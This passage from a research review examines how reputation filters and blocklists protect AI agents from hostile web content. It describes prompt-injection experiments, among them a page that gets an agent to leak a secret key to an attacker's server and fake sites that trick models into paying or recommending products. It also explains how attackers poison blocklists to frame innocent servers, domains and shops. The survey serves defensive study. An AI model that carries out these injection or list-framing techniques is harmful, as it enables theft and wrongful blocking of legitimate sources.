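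The services returned more than 282,000 results. In 534 searches, the results included content already known to be malicious. The rate ranged from 0.8% of searches on the safest service to 2.2% on the worst. If each service received every query, the average was about 1.4%, and an agent that ran 50 searches would have had roughly an even chance of being offered at least one such result, though it might not have opened it. This rate is far higher than the April survey's one host in 87,000, but the two figures aren't directly comparable, because the benchmark counts searches rather than hosts and includes malware and lookalike package names as well as planted instructions.

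A reputation filter could in principle have caught all 534, since somebody had already identified the content. The search services evidently didn't remove it. The benchmark is therefore the best evidence so far that existing lists could help coding agents if someone applied them to search results. It doesn't measure how much those lists would miss, because it counts only content that somebody has identified. Faisal also notes that AIR hasn't released its queries or scanner, so outsiders can't yet check what it classed as malicious.

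### Hostile text under a good name

Attackers don't need to build a reputation if they can put text on a respected site. The simplest way to do this is to post a comment, although comments made up only 1.8% of the instructions in the April survey. The share is probably higher on the web as a whole, because Common Crawl contains little social media. A single comment on a busy page may also reach more agents than a thousand pages on an obscure site.

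Code-hosting sites offer attackers a better opportunity, because coding agents visit them constantly and expect to find commands there. *Web Hole attack targets AI agents via abandoned sites* (Lagonsin, 2026) reports that an earlier study by AIR found a GitHub repository with malicious commands in its README, the file that explains how to install and use a project. A filter that trusts github.com as a whole admits this file, while one that judges the account or repository could refuse it, although a new account has no record to judge.

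A respected site can also direct agents to unsafe content by mistake. Many companies now publish files called llms.txt, which tell AI agents how to read their websites. TechRadar's *Top AI tools including Claude, Codex, and Hermes installed suspicious code* describes a study of 6,214 domains belonging to defence contractors, Fortune 500 companies and large technology firms. On 120 of them, or about 2%, such a file pointed to a code package or domain that nobody had registered. Some names may have been typos, and others may have belonged to abandoned projects. Anyone could register one of these names, and the company's file would then direct agents to it. The researchers registered some as an experiment, and TechRadar reports that AI tools installed suspicious code inside corporate networks.

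A source filter that checks only the first site would miss this, because the company's file is genuine. The filter would have to check the package or domain named in the file, and not count the file's recommendation as evidence of safety.

### Lapsed domains

When a site's owner stops paying for its domain, anyone can register the name, but search engines may continue to rank it as before. In October 2026, AIR Security reported a test in which it compiled about 2,000 queries that an AI assistant might make and checked roughly 6,500 sites in the results. Thirty-six, about one in 180, had domains that were no longer registered. They included pyquestions.com and thestackoverflow.com, whose name resembles that of the programming site Stack Overflow. Antipov (2026), in *Домен умер, но поисковик о нём помнит*, writes that these two came up for questions about a web-programming feature and a Python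 error.

An attacker could buy such a name, put instructions on the page and wait for agents to arrive. This would avoid the main expense of rotating sources to target agents, which is getting a new site noticed. A name that already ranks might cost no more than the ordinary registration fee.

AIR showed that attackers could exploit these domains, but Antipov points out that the company gave no evidence of mass break-ins through them. The 36 sites had no owner, and therefore no hostile content, when AIR checked them.

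Criminals do buy lapsed domains to deceive people, however. The Hacker News' *Domain Security* reports that, according to the security firm Infoblox, attackers had spent nearly $7 million on expired domains, hoping to inherit their visitors and reputation and redirect people to scams and malware. ThaiCERT's *Threat Actors Found Buying Expired Domains to Use as Infrastructure for Cyberattacks* reports that 20% of domains registered in the first half of the year, or about 65,000 a day, had been used before. Most of the buyers may be harmless, since a good name also has legitimate uses. ThaiCERT warns that security software may rate these domains as low risk because of their history.

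A reputation filter should therefore attach a good record to the owner of a domain and not just to its name. It could drop the record whenever the registration lapses and treat the name as new. This would be unfair to an owner who renewed a few days late, but the harm seems minor. Sales are harder to detect, because a domain can be sold without lapsing and registration records often don't show who owns it.

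Language models sometimes invent plausible web addresses that no one has ever owned, and an attacker can register them before agents visit. Unit 42 ran 685,339 queries about 913 well-known brands on two models and collected 2.1 million addresses. More than 13,000 were confirmed as malicious, and about 250,000 of the invented domains were still available to register. In one case, attackers began using an invented domain 23 days after Unit 42 predicted they might. A filter that distrusts new domains would block invented ones because they have no good record to inherit, but it might admit a lapsed domain that does.

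### Bought popularity

Coding agents also choose software packages and "skills", which are sets of instructions for performing a task. A public registry may hold thousands of them from authors the user has never heard of, so an agent might rely on popularity signals such as stars, download counts or mentions in other projects.

Signals that count every account or request equally are vulnerable to Sybil attacks. One person can give stars from many accounts, and a script can download the same package repeatedly.

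Mentions of a domain can mislead a reputation filter even when nobody bought them. *Placeholder Domains Used by 349 AI Agent Skills Found Redirecting to Scams* (Ahmed, 2026) reports that some visitors to placeholder domains, which programmers had used as made-up addresses in examples, ended up at scams. The security company Manifold Security found these domains in 359,000 files on GitHub and in 349 agent skills. The programmers were probably copying a convenient example, but a filter that counted mentions as endorsements would have rated the domains very highly.

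Attackers also work to obtain high search rankings, another form of popularity, as in the two impostor-site campaigns. AIR's benchmark found a malicious page built to rank first for queries about cryptocurrency projects. Faisal says the page was linked to known malware campaigns.

The price of faking a signal matters more than whether someone can fake it. Suppose, with invented figures, that fake stars cost ten cents each and an agent installs only packages with at least 1,000. Each malicious package would then cost an attacker another $100. As with the price of domains, that would deter an attacker who earns a few dollars from each package, but not one seeking a company password worth $1,000, who would break even if one package in ten succeeded. Raising the threshold to 10,000 stars would deter that attacker too, but it would also exclude most small, honest projects. Counting only stars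 from accounts the user's company already has reason to trust would raise the attacker's cost without requiring a huge audience, although a new project would still have to wait for someone with a trusted account to find it.

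## Controlled tests of source trust in agents

To measure how much a filter would help agents that open hostile pages, researchers have to give the same agent the same hostile page repeatedly and change only how the agent treats the source. They can use surveys to count hostile pages, but not to measure this effect.

### Allowlists on outgoing requests

In *Silent Egress*, Lan, Kaul and colleagues (February 2026) tested an outbound filter this way. They built an agent on qwen2.5:7b, a small open model, put a secret key in its context and asked it to summarise a web page. The page contained an instruction to send the key to an attacker's server, supposedly to verify the connection. In 480 runs without defences, the agent contacted that server 88% of the time, and in 95% of those cases its summary to the user looked harmless. In 120 runs with harmless pages, it never contacted the server.

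They then ran one version of the attack 30 times with each of several defences.

| Defence | Agent tried to send data | Data reached the attacker |
|---|---|---|
| None | 100% | 100% |
| Warning in the agent's instructions | 67% | 67% |
| Tags marking the page as untrusted | 100% | 100% |
| Warning and tags | 57% | 57% |
| Allowlist of four domains | 100% | 0% |

With the allowlist, the page still fooled the agent every time, but a program outside the model blocked the request. The program allowed requests to only four domains, and the attacker's domain, evil-collector.net, wasn't one of them. Thirty runs is a small sample, but more would add little, because the request could get through only if the program had a bug.

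Another filter, which blocked suspicious-looking addresses, also stopped every leak, but this result is less reassuring. One of its rules blocked any path containing "collect". The paper's sample attack sends data to /collect, and an attacker could avoid that rule by renaming the path.

An allowlist also has an advantage over filters that search outgoing requests for secrets. In half of the 480 runs, the page told the agent to split the key into four pieces and send them separately. The agent contacted the server in 77% of these runs instead of 99%, but each piece looked more like ordinary data. An allowlist should stop the pieces as easily as the whole key because it ignores what a request contains, although the researchers didn't test an allowlist against split keys.

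Lan and colleagues explain that an allowlist would be harder to use in practice because an attacker could send the data through a hacked site on the list, take over an abandoned subdomain of a trusted company, or use a trusted site's redirect link. Their simulated attacker did none of these things.

They also didn't measure the loss of useful work, which is probably the bigger obstacle. Three of the four permitted domains belonged to a fictional company, and the fourth was example.com. An agent limited to those domains could summarise a page the system had already fetched, but it couldn't order flowers or check a second source.

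### Weighting pages by search rank

An assistant that reads several pages before answering can compare them. *ReliabilityRAG* (Shen, Imana and colleagues, 2025) uses such comparisons to filter documents in retrieval-augmented generation (RAG), where a program finds documents and a language model answers from them. The basic method has five steps.

1. The search returns a ranked list of documents.
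2. The model answers the question from each document separately. The program drops documents that don't help.
3. A second model compares every pair of answers and marks those that contradict each other.
4. The program finds the largest group of documents with no contradictions. If two groups are equally large, it prefers the one with higher-ranked documents.
5. The model answers the question again, using only that group.

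Suppose a user asks whether a camera is waterproof. The pages ranked first, second and fourth say no, and a hostile page in third place says yes. The three honest pages form the largest consistent group, so the model writes the final answer without the hostile page. If a second hostile page replaced the one in fourth place, the groups would tie at two pages each, and the honest group would win because its pages rank higher. If the hostile pages ranked first and third instead, the attacker would win the tie.

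For longer lists, Shen and colleagues give each document a weight. In their main tests with 50 documents, each document's weight was 10% lower than that of the one above it, so the first carried about 10% of the total and the last about 0.06%. The program drew two documents at random according to these weights, had the model answer from them, and repeated this 20 times. It then looked for the largest consistent group among the 20 answers.

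The table shows Mistral-7B's results on 100 questions about recent news, with one hostile document among the 50. The second column is calculated from the weights.

| Rank of hostile document | Chance of being drawn at least once | In the final set | Correct answers with the filter | Correct answers without it |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | 99% | 61.4% | 55.2% | 38.8% |
| 25 | 28% | 12.3% | 69.0% | 21.2% |
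| 50 | 2% | 0.8% | 71.8% | 9.2% |

The filter almost always removes a hostile document at the bottom of the list but often keeps one at the top. When the hostile document came first, two rival defences that ignore rank stopped more attacks than the filter did. Shen and colleagues accept this weakness because they expect the top position to be much harder for attackers to reach.

Their experiment didn't test that expectation, because they placed the hostile text at each rank themselves. The ranks also had little to do with reputation. The researchers took snippets from Google results and used a model to reorder them by how well each one matched the question. A hostile page written for a particular question could score very well. The impostor sites described earlier had also been pushed up real search results, and this method is weakest against such sites.

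The method is mathematically guaranteed to select the honest pages when they are in the majority, provided that they all agree and the second model detects every contradiction between an honest page and a hostile one. Under those conditions, no consistent group can contain both kinds of page. The method therefore suits questions of fact better than shopping, where two honest reviewers may recommend different cameras. For questions with several valid answers, it would follow the highest-ranked pages.

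Even for factual questions, the correct answer may have little support among the retrieved documents. On average, only 26% of the documents retrieved for the news questions contained it word for word. That is two or three pages out of ten, so three hostile pages might be enough to outvote them.

The extra work takes little time. With Mistral-7B, it raised the median time per question from 0.17 to 0.61 seconds for ten documents and from 0.25 to 1.32 seconds for fifty.

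### Weighting sources by their past answers

Search rank is weak evidence of how a source has behaved. In *Retrieval-Augmented Generation with Estimation of Source Reliability*, Hwang, Park and colleagues (2024) instead estimate how often each source is right, without having people check its claims. Their method starts by giving all sources equal weight and collecting each source's answers to the same set of test questions. A weighted vote then picks one answer to each question. A source's reliability score is the share of its answers that match those picked. The method recalculates the weights from these scores and repeats the vote until the weights settle.

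When a user asks a question, the sources vote with their final weights. In one example, the question was when the eighth season of the television series *Shameless* would begin, and three of six sources had an answer. Each vote's weight is six times the source's estimated reliability, minus one.

| Answer | Estimated reliability | Weight of vote |
|---|---|---|
| November 2018 | 0.26 | 0.56 |
| November 2018 | 0.32 | 0.92 |
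| November 2017 (correct) | 0.89 | 4.34 |

A simple majority would choose 2018, but the weighted vote chooses 2017 by 4.34 to 1.48.

Hwang and colleagues also tested the scoring method on real sources, using Google News to check their claims. For one politician, the method estimated that 17.5% of 388 claims were true, while the fact-checking site PolitiFact had rated 16.5% true. For an account posting breaking news, the estimate was 66% and the true figure was 74%. The results are encouraging, but the method did worse on recent news because fewer other sources had covered it. Claims about a new camera from a small maker would be hard to check for the same reason.

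Since all sources start with equal weight, the first round is a majority vote. In a Sybil attack where one attacker runs five of nine sites and gives the same false answers on each, those sites will earn high scores and the honest sites low ones. Hwang and colleagues simulated up to seven mostly false sources out of nine, and their method performed much better than majority voting, but sources that coordinate their false answers would be a harder test.

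A simpler approach is to set the scores by hand. In *Source-Aware Reranking for Retrieval-Augmented Generation*, Koganti and Garrido-Lestache Belinchon (2026) multiplied each document's relevance by a score for its type, from 0.95 for peer-reviewed research to 0.30 for AI-generated text. They tested this on ten health questions and 120 documents, ten of them hostile. The share of relevant documents in the top five rose from 48% to 72%, but the number of times hostile documents appeared across all ten questions fell only from 16 to 14, and results got worse for two questions. Every hostile document in the test was labelled as AI-generated or user-written. An attacker who could get a document labelled "government" would benefit from the scores instead.

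### Models as their own judges

Developers could skip the list and let the model decide whether a site looks trustworthy. In July 2026, Zscaler tested this on 26 models, using the two fake sites it had found. The first site claimed that a programmer needed a $3 licence key to fix an error. In a sandbox with no real money and no spending limit, four models paid: two versions of Llama, Gemini 3 Flash and Gemini 2.5 Pro.

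The second site, debank.auction, imitated the cryptocurrency service DeBank. Zscaler asked the models which addresses were trustworthy and varied what else they could see.

- When they also had the official DeBank site, none of the 26 accepted the fake.
- When they had other web pages but not the official site, GPT-5.4 accepted it.
- When they had only the fake site, Claude Sonnet 4.5 accepted it.

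The official site may have helped by giving the models something to compare the fake with, as a single allowlist entry would. But only one model failed in each of the other conditions, and Zscaler doesn't report how often it ran each model, so the difference could be chance. Zscaler also sells web security, and its post lists the name under which its product detects these threats, so it has a reason to publicise the failures. However, the overall result it reports isn't alarming, since 22 of 26 models refused to pay.

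Larger experiments suggest that models are fairly good at ignoring hidden commands but worse at judging evidence. In *How Much Can We Trust LLM Search Agents?*, Chen, Ren and colleagues (2026) asked 13 models 44 questions about health, finance, law and consumer technology. They replaced up to three of the ten search results with invented pages promoting a product. Hidden instructions got the product recommended in 0.3% of cases. A single page made to look like an institution's succeeded in 14.2% of cases, and three pages that seemed to agree independently succeeded in 24.8%. The most effective attack combined an official-looking page, a review citing it and a forum post citing both, and it succeeded in 37.2% of cases.

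Claude Sonnet 4.6 never recommended the product in 264 attacks, while Gemini 3 Flash did so in 31.4% of them. Against Gemini 3 Flash, the attack using apparently independent pages succeeded 39% of the time with one page, 55% with two and 77% with three. Moving the pages up or down the results made no significant difference, so this model didn't seem to use rank as a sign of reliability.

A cautious model can also reject honest sources. Chen and colleagues asked models ten questions about add-ons for OpenClaw, a real AI assistant. Claude Sonnet 4.6 wrongly dismissed OpenClaw or its add-ons in eight of the ten cases when there was no attack. GPT-5.4-mini made no such mistake, but when the researchers added pages promoting an invented add-on, it gave the user the command to install the add-on in all ten cases. A test that measured only successful attacks would have found no errors by Claude.

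Asking a model to check its own answer may not help much either. On consumer technology questions where an attack had succeeded, the models rated the credibility of their own answers at 0.61 out of 1 on average. A separate model with no information about the attack rated the same answers at 0.30.

### Claimed authority and familiar names

Attacks on agents work partly because any page can claim authority. *When Bots Take the Bait* (2026) reports that removing words such as "official", "government" and "bank" from hostile pages, while leaving everything else unchanged, reduced the attacks' average success rate by 14.3%.

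In *Whose Facts Win?*, Schuster, Gautam and Markert (2026) isolated the effect of the source more carefully. They gave 13 open models pairs of contradictory facts, each attributed to an invented source. The facts were about invented people, buildings and products, so the models couldn't rely on what they already knew. The models generally favoured government agencies over newspapers, and newspapers over private individuals and social media users. They also favoured newspapers with a larger circulation and accounts with more followers, and an attacker can make up both figures.

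Repetition could reverse these preferences. When the social media version appeared twice, all 13 models preferred it to the government's, even if both copies came from the same account. When the researchers named two accounts above a single copy, the models kept their original preference. The repeated text seems to have mattered more than the number of accounts posting it.

Chen and colleagues found the opposite on Gemini 3 Flash. Repeating one institution's page had almost no effect, and only adding sources made a difference. The experiments used different models, and Schuster and colleagues made the model choose between two answers, while Chen and colleagues let it write a recommendation. Removing duplicate pages before the model reads them would be an easy precaution, but it wouldn't stop an attacker who writes three different pages.

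Where planted instructions appear also affects how well they work. *Where You Inject Matters* (2026) found that they were generally more effective on GitHub and in the chat program Slack than in the workplace tools Confluence and Jira, although success rates there were fairly low. In another group of tasks, they worked best in web pages and reviews, which is a concern for shopping agents.

### Provenance instead of reputation

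*ROPE* (Ma, Xiao and colleagues, 2026) presents a defence that uses only provenance (who wrote something), not reputation (how that party has behaved). It applies when an agent is about to do something with consequences, such as sending money after a user asks it to pay the invoice in Alice's latest email.

1. Before the agent reads any outside content, a language model reads the user's request and sets a rule for each sensitive detail. In this case, the account number must come from the request itself or from Alice.
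2. As the agent works, a program labels each text with its origin. It counts an email as Alice's only if the mail system has authenticated the sender, whatever name the message displays.
3. Before the payment, another program checks that the account number appears in full in an accepted text. If it doesn't, the program blocks the payment.

The final check doesn't use a language model, so a hostile page can't get past it with persuasive text. The page may still mislead the agent, but an account number found only on that page will fail the check.

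Ma and colleagues measured how much defences reduce useful work, which the *Silent Egress* experiment did not. On AgentDyn, a set of test tasks for agents, GPT-4o-mini without a defence completed 46.7% of the tasks when nobody was attacking, and attacks succeeded 49.6% of the time. With ROPE, it completed 36.7% of the tasks when nobody was attacking, and attacks succeeded 0.3% of the time. ROPE reduced the number of completed tasks by about a fifth. Three other defences reduced it much more, and the agent completed only 18.3%, 15.0% and 6.7% of the tasks with them. The agent was weak to begin with, so these figures are more useful for comparing defences than for predicting how much a current agent's completion rate would drop.

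ROPE checks whether the origin is genuine and whether the user authorised that source for this purpose. Neither check depends on the source's record. An advertisement with a valid digital signature has a genuine origin but no authority to choose where the user's money goes, and the same is true of a respected newspaper. A supplier that opened last week has no reputation, but if the user names it, the agent needs its account number.

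Reputation is more useful when the user doesn't know whom to trust. If a fraudster has persuaded the user to name a fake supplier, ROPE would accept the supplier's authenticated account number, while a blocklist might include the supplier's domain. Neither would necessarily help if someone had broken into Alice's email account, because the message would come from her real account and she would have a good record as a sender.

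ROPE also doesn't cover attacks that only mislead the user through the agent's reply, as the fake camera page does.

### Live lists, adaptive attackers and long tasks

None of these experiments put an agent behind a live blocklist. The researchers fixed the permitted domains, ranks, rules or scores before the test began. Their results therefore don't cover the hours or days before a real blocklist includes a new malicious site.

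Few of the attackers adapted to the scores either. Shen and colleagues tried one attack designed to get past their contradiction check. If the correct answer was A and the attacker wanted B, the hostile document told the model to answer "A or B", which doesn't clearly contradict A. When this document ranked first, it reached the final set 72.4% of the time instead of 61.4%. Accuracy didn't fall, because the model often chose A anyway. Shen and colleagues didn't test a more direct attack, in which a document leads the model to the right answer when read alone but the wrong one when read with others.

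An attacker can also earn a good score honestly and then exploit it. A site could answer all of Hwang and colleagues' test questions correctly and lie only about the product it sells. Hwang and colleagues acknowledge a similar danger, that a hacker could take over a reliable account between score updates. Agents may also come to trust a site without any score. *The Long Con on the Web* (Xu, Dong and colleagues, 2026) found that coding agents were more likely to follow a site's harmful instructions after the site had given them useful help.

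That pattern can appear only in tasks with several steps, and most of the experiments ended after a single answer or request. ROPE is an exception, because Ma and colleagues also tested it against attacks spread over long tasks, and those attacks failed too. Its rules stay the same throughout a task, so a site can't gain permission to supply an account number by being helpful first.

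## Experiments and incidents in which lists were poisoned

The agents in those experiments used lists and scores that stayed fixed during each test. A live list changes whenever its operator receives new evidence. Operators seldom see a source do harm, so they rely on sensors, such as a spamtrap that receives a message, a user who files a complaint or a server that logs a connection. An attacker who can feed those sensors false evidence can change the list without hacking it.

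An attacker can poison a list to make a harmless source look malicious or a malicious one look harmless. Most documented cases are of the first kind, perhaps because the owners of falsely flagged sources complain, while a malicious site with a clean record attracts no attention.

*Is Crunching Public Data the Right Approach to Detect BGP Hijacks?* (2025) describes how an attacker could poison the data used to detect hijacks in internet routing. Networks announce to each other which addresses they can reach, and a rogue network can hijack traffic by announcing addresses that belong to someone else. Some defences learn from public monitors which networks normally connect to each other, and treat unfamiliar connections as suspicious. An attacker could announce a false connection in advance, using addresses the attacker really owns, so that the monitors record it. A later hijack that used the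 same connection would then look normal to the defences.

### The HADES experiment

The most thorough test of framing is *HADES Attack* (Li, Lu and colleagues, 2025), which examined 29 email blocklist providers. The providers used three kinds of sensor.

- Spamtraps are either new addresses that nobody has used or old ones that their owners abandoned.
- Relay servers filter incoming mail for a provider's customers, and the provider watches that traffic for spammers.
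- Shared data comes from partner organisations, which send the provider their mail logs or their own lists of threats.

Providers keep their traps secret, but Li and colleagues found that outsiders can recognise many of them because they behave differently from ordinary mailboxes. An attacker who knows of a trap can poison a list without sending any spam, by getting an innocent server to send something to the trap. The attacker can do this from three positions.

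- An insider has an account with the victim's mail service and writes to the trap. The message leaves through servers that the other customers also use.
- An outsider gets the victim's website to write to the trap, because many sites send newsletters or password resets to whatever address a visitor supplies.
- A forger sends mail from another machine but puts the victim's domain in it. This frames the domain and not the IP address.

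To test this, the researchers set up their own mail servers and domains, sent harmless messages to suspected sensors and watched the lists. Fourteen of the 29 providers listed these servers or domains. Spamtraps worked against 13 providers, relay servers against six and shared data against at least two. The table gives some of the results, averaged over three runs.

| List | Time until listing | Time until automatic removal |
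|---|---|---|
| Spamhaus, IP addresses | 3 minutes | 7 days |
| Brukalai, IP addresses | 1 hour | 30 days |
| SpamCop, IP addresses | 3 hours | 3 days, on and off |
| Spamhaus, domains | 6 hours | 14 days |
| Senderscore, IP addresses | 12 hours | 10 days |
| Surriel, IP addresses | 24 hours | 14 days |

Three messages were enough to put a server on Spamhaus's list for a week. Three providers, including Spamhaus, also listed domains that appeared only in forged messages, even though those messages failed the standard checks for forged senders.

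The test servers were new and had no record of sending good mail. A provider might require more than three stray messages before listing a server that has sent millions of wanted ones. Li and colleagues doubt that age matters much, because lists often include prominent mail servers. But some of those servers may have sent spam from hacked accounts, so their presence on a list doesn't show that they would be as easy to frame as the new servers.

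An incident at Coremail, a large Chinese mail company, suggests that established servers are vulnerable too. On 6 February 2023, Coremail's customers sent 1,690 messages to Spamhaus's traps. The same day, other servers rejected 476,108 messages from Coremail, about 25 times the daily average, because its servers were on Spamhaus's lists. Li and colleagues blame the messages to the traps for the rejections. Over the 15 months of records, the most common trap addresses were misspellings of real ones. A hacked account sending spam that day could have caused both the trap messages and the rejections, but if Li and colleagues are right, typing errors got a major company's mail blocked, and an attacker could do the same on purpose.

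### Large victims and deleted domains

Blocklist operators can protect important senders with an internal allowlist. To see how many senders were protected, Li and colleagues checked 50,987 outgoing mail servers of popular websites and mail services every 12 hours for two months. About 77% appeared on at least one blocklist, so the operators of those lists evidently hadn't allowlisted them. That figure overstates the danger, because some of the lists have very few users. Spamhaus, by far the most widely used, listed 17% of the servers. About half of the popular domains sent their mail through fewer than 20 servers, so an attacker wouldn't have to frame many servers to disrupt a domain's mail.

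A framed domain could lose its website as well as its email. Registries, the companies that run domain endings such as .xyz and .store, sometimes suspend domains that appear on blocklists. Li and colleagues followed newly registered domains for a month and found 11 endings under which the registry had suspended more than half of the blocklisted domains. The four registries responsible run 51 endings in all. A forger might therefore be able to take a victim's website offline by sending a few emails in the victim's name. The researchers didn't test this, and a registry might look more carefully before suspending an established business than a domain registered last week.

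Five of the 14 providers acknowledged the problem. Spfbl promised to fix it, SpamCop and Mailspike said the cost would make defences difficult, and Gbudb and Surbl said they were not significantly affected. The low interest is unsurprising, since the provider would pay for better sensors while the framed sender suffers most of the damage.

### Votes and ratings

PhishTank relies on volunteers to report suspicious addresses and vote on whether each one is phishing. *Evaluating the Wisdom of Crowds in Assessing Phishing Websites* (Moore and Clayton, 2008) examined about 176,000 completed decisions from 2007 and considered how an attacker might corrupt them. A selfish attacker would vote to clear their own phishing pages. An undermining attacker would report legitimate sites and vote to condemn them, to make people stop trusting the list.

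Moore and Clayton found no proof that anyone had done either. They identified 161 users who disagreed with other voters in most of their votes, and these users voted on the same reports nearly 90 times as often as chance would predict. This could indicate a conspiracy, or one person with many accounts, but the researchers thought it more likely that honest people were making the same mistakes. Volunteers did wrongly label 39 sites as phishing, including eBay's main address, before later votes reversed the decisions.

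The obvious rules against manipulation didn't suit PhishTank.

- A cap on votes would hold back the most useful volunteers, because 25 moderators cast 74% of all votes. An attacker could get around it by registering more accounts.
- A requirement to vote correctly several times first would be easy to meet. About 97% of the reported addresses were phishing, so a user could build an excellent record by voting "phish" every time.
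- A ban on users with many mistakes would catch the most active contributors. The top submitter also had the most invalid reports, 578.
- A ban on users who were wrong in more than 5% of their reports would exclude 44% of submitters and 5% of the valid reports, while an attacker could dilute a bad record with easy ones.

Moore and Clayton's best suggestion was to rely on the moderators alone during a suspected attack. Their objection to trusting users with a good record applies even more strongly to agents that judge websites. If only one host in 87,000 carries hostile instructions, an agent that calls every host harmless will be right more than 99.99% of the time. A list operator who trusted reporters based on their overall accuracy would trust that agent completely, even when it vouched for its owner's scam site.

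Web of Trust, a browser add-on, asks its users to rate sites. Chia and Knapskog (2012), in *Re-evaluating the Wisdom of Crowds in Assessing Web Security*, found that it identified bad domains more comprehensively than three automated services, although a few users again did much of the rating. The company told a critic on Mozilla's *Anmeldelser af Web of Trust, MyWOT/WOT*, a Danish-language review page, that its algorithm lets only trustworthy users influence a rating. One user complains on Mozilla's *Reviews for Web of Trust, MyWOT/WOT* that scammers now rate phishing sites as reputable. This single complaint gives no examples, so it is weak evidence of an organised campaign, and the company describes its algorithm too briefly for outsiders to judge how well it would resist one.

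### Forged traffic against Tor

In late 2024, an attacker framed innocent machines on the Tor network. Tor hides its users' locations by passing their traffic through relays, most of which volunteers run on rented servers. According to *Defending the Tor network* (gus, 2024), the Tor Project's own account, someone sent connection requests to machines across the internet and forged the return addresses so that the requests seemed to come from Tor relays. From 20 October, monitoring systems at the receiving end sent automatic complaints to the companies that hosted the relays.

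The sender of the first packet of an internet connection can forge its return address. The reply then goes to the forged address, so the forger never sees it and normally can't complete the connection. According to Osservatorio Nessuno's *Censorship Attack against the Tor network* (2024), the complaints reported many failed login attempts, but most of the accused relays had sent no such traffic. Nobody can try a password before the connection is complete, so the complaints probably described login attempts that never happened. Proulx (2024), in *Tor relays source IPs spoofed to mass-scan port 22?*, mentions a complaint of "port scanning" based on three packets.

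Some hosting companies blocked or suspended the accused relays. The Tor Project says that a few relays went offline temporarily and that users noticed nothing. Investigators traced the forged packets with help from the security company GreyNoise and had the source shut down on 7 November. Some operators still had to persuade their hosts to restore their accounts. The Tor Project believes the attacker wanted to get the relays onto blocklists.

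Rapid7 (2020) estimated that more than 100 million source addresses had appeared in one pattern of earlier traffic of this kind between January and May 2020. The company believed the addresses were forged, partly because the largest known botnets had perhaps 10 million machines. A list that counted each packet as evidence against its source address would have wrongly listed most or all of them.

False complaints also make real ones less useful. In *Re: A plea to ignore abuse reports* (Corallo, 2024), a message to a mailing list for network operators, Corallo writes that large hosting companies receive so many worthless automated complaints that they can't investigate them. He discards complaints from any network that won't answer his questions. *Someone is attacking Tor right now* quotes GreyNoise's Andrew Morris, who advised hosting companies during the attack to ignore all scanning complaints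 about a published set of Tor addresses. His advice was sensible as a temporary measure, but anyone who controlled one of those machines could then have scanned other networks with little risk.

### Defences and what they cost

A list operator can check that evidence comes from the source it incriminates. Email authentication would stop the forger in the HADES study, and a monitoring system could ignore any address that hasn't completed a connection, though it would then miss some real scanners that deliberately leave connections incomplete. Authentication would not stop the insider or the outsider, because the victim's own server sends the incriminating message.

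Reading the messages that reach an operator's traps would help more against those two. In the outsider's attack, the operator would find newsletters and password resets, not advertisements for counterfeit pills. Li and colleagues recommend this kind of review, along with requiring evidence from several sensors. They also advise receivers to consult more than one list, but their results suggest that this wouldn't help much. A single five-hour run of test messages put their servers or domains on the lists of 13 providers, so a receiver that required two lists to agree could still have blocked the mail.

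Waiting for more evidence also gives real attackers more time. PhishTank's voters confirmed phishing pages about 16 hours later, on average, than the staff of a company with its own list did. That delay would be long enough for the hostile camera site in the earlier example, which had to stay up for ten hours to earn back the price of its domain.

Limits on each reporter's influence are easy to set but depend on knowing who the reporters are. ClawHub's *MoltThreats* describes a live feed of threats that AI agents both read and contribute to. The feed appears to limit each agent to 20 reports a day, and it publishes a warning only after several agents have observed the same behaviour and a human has reviewed it. But one person can run many agents. According to Fortune (2026), the security firm Wiz found that about 17,000 people controlled the 1.5 million agents on Moltbook, a social network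 for AI agents, or 88 each on average. Someone with 88 agents on the threat feed could file 1,760 reports a day and meet the requirement for several agents without anyone else's help. Human review is probably the stronger protection. It is slower, but agents fetch the feed only every two days anyway.

Notifying a source before listing it gives an innocent source the chance to object. ClawHub, a marketplace for add-ons to the AI assistant OpenClaw, similarly warns publishers whose accounts look abusive. According to OpenClaw's *Moderation and Account Safety*, the warning is automatic, and ClawHub may act against the account if a scan after the deadline still finds a problem. Notice is useless against a phishing page that exists for ten minutes. The delay matters less for planted instructions, many of which stay online for months, and an honest shop that received a warning could delete the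 offending review, though a dishonest one could show the list's crawler a clean version of the page. The operator could reduce this risk by blocking the single page at once and giving notice only before it blocks the whole domain.

Quick expiry limits the damage from each false entry, but the attacker can frame the victim again. Repeating the attack once a week might keep a server on a list whose entries last seven days. Many providers also keep repeat offenders listed for longer or refuse them early removal. This makes sense against spammers, but it also means that a framed sender is treated worse after each attack. Quick expiry also removes correct entries. If a page with hostile instructions stays up for a year and each entry lasts a week, the list's operator has to detect the page again about 50 times to keep it listed.

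### If agents report attacks automatically

If agents automatically report the injections they find to a shared blocklist, a camera shop's competitor might get the shop blocked. The competitor would post a review on the shop's site containing hidden instructions for AI systems. Visiting agents would detect the instructions and report the domain, and every agent that used the list would stop opening the shop's pages.

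Nobody seems to have published a test of framing a website by planting instructions on it for agents to report, so the chances of success can only be inferred. It looks easier than framing a mail server in several respects. The attacker doesn't have to find a secret trap, because any visiting agent can report the page. An operator who checks the report will find the instructions there, just as the agents said. The agents only have to notice the text, so a crude command that every current model would refuse to obey is ideal, and better detectors would make the framing more reliable.

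Authentication can't detect this trick, because the page does come from the shop's server. The operator needs to know who wrote the text. An automatic rule that listed every host Khodayari and colleagues found in the web archive would have penalized more than a third of those hosts' operators for text other people wrote.

Listing the account that posted the text would be fairer if the account's owner really posted it. *Risks and Controls for Multi-Agent Systems* (2026) reports that Moltbook once let anyone edit any existing post without logging in. An attacker could have put hostile instructions under a respected author's name or changed a post after a reviewer had approved it.

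An attacker might also hijack the agents that file reports and use them to file false ones. The same paper cites an assessment that found 506 attempted injections on Moltbook in 72 hours, 60 of them duplicate posts from one actor. According to the Institute for Security and Technology's *Lessons from Moltbook*, an injection there could push an agent into "upvoting posts, following accounts, or making API calls". Similar instructions could perhaps make an agent accuse a rival or vouch for a scam. Reports from a hundred companies' agents would then look independent even though one attacker was behind them all.

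To prevent this, the MoltThreats feed requires the user's approval for every report. But in an automatic review, ClawHub rated the add-on "suspicious" with medium confidence and noted that its stated rules don't match its marketplace settings. Unless the platform stops the model from using the add-on unprompted, the agent has to enforce the approval rule on itself, and a hijacked agent is the least likely to do so. In the same review, ClawHub advises users to have a way to override the feed's false positives.

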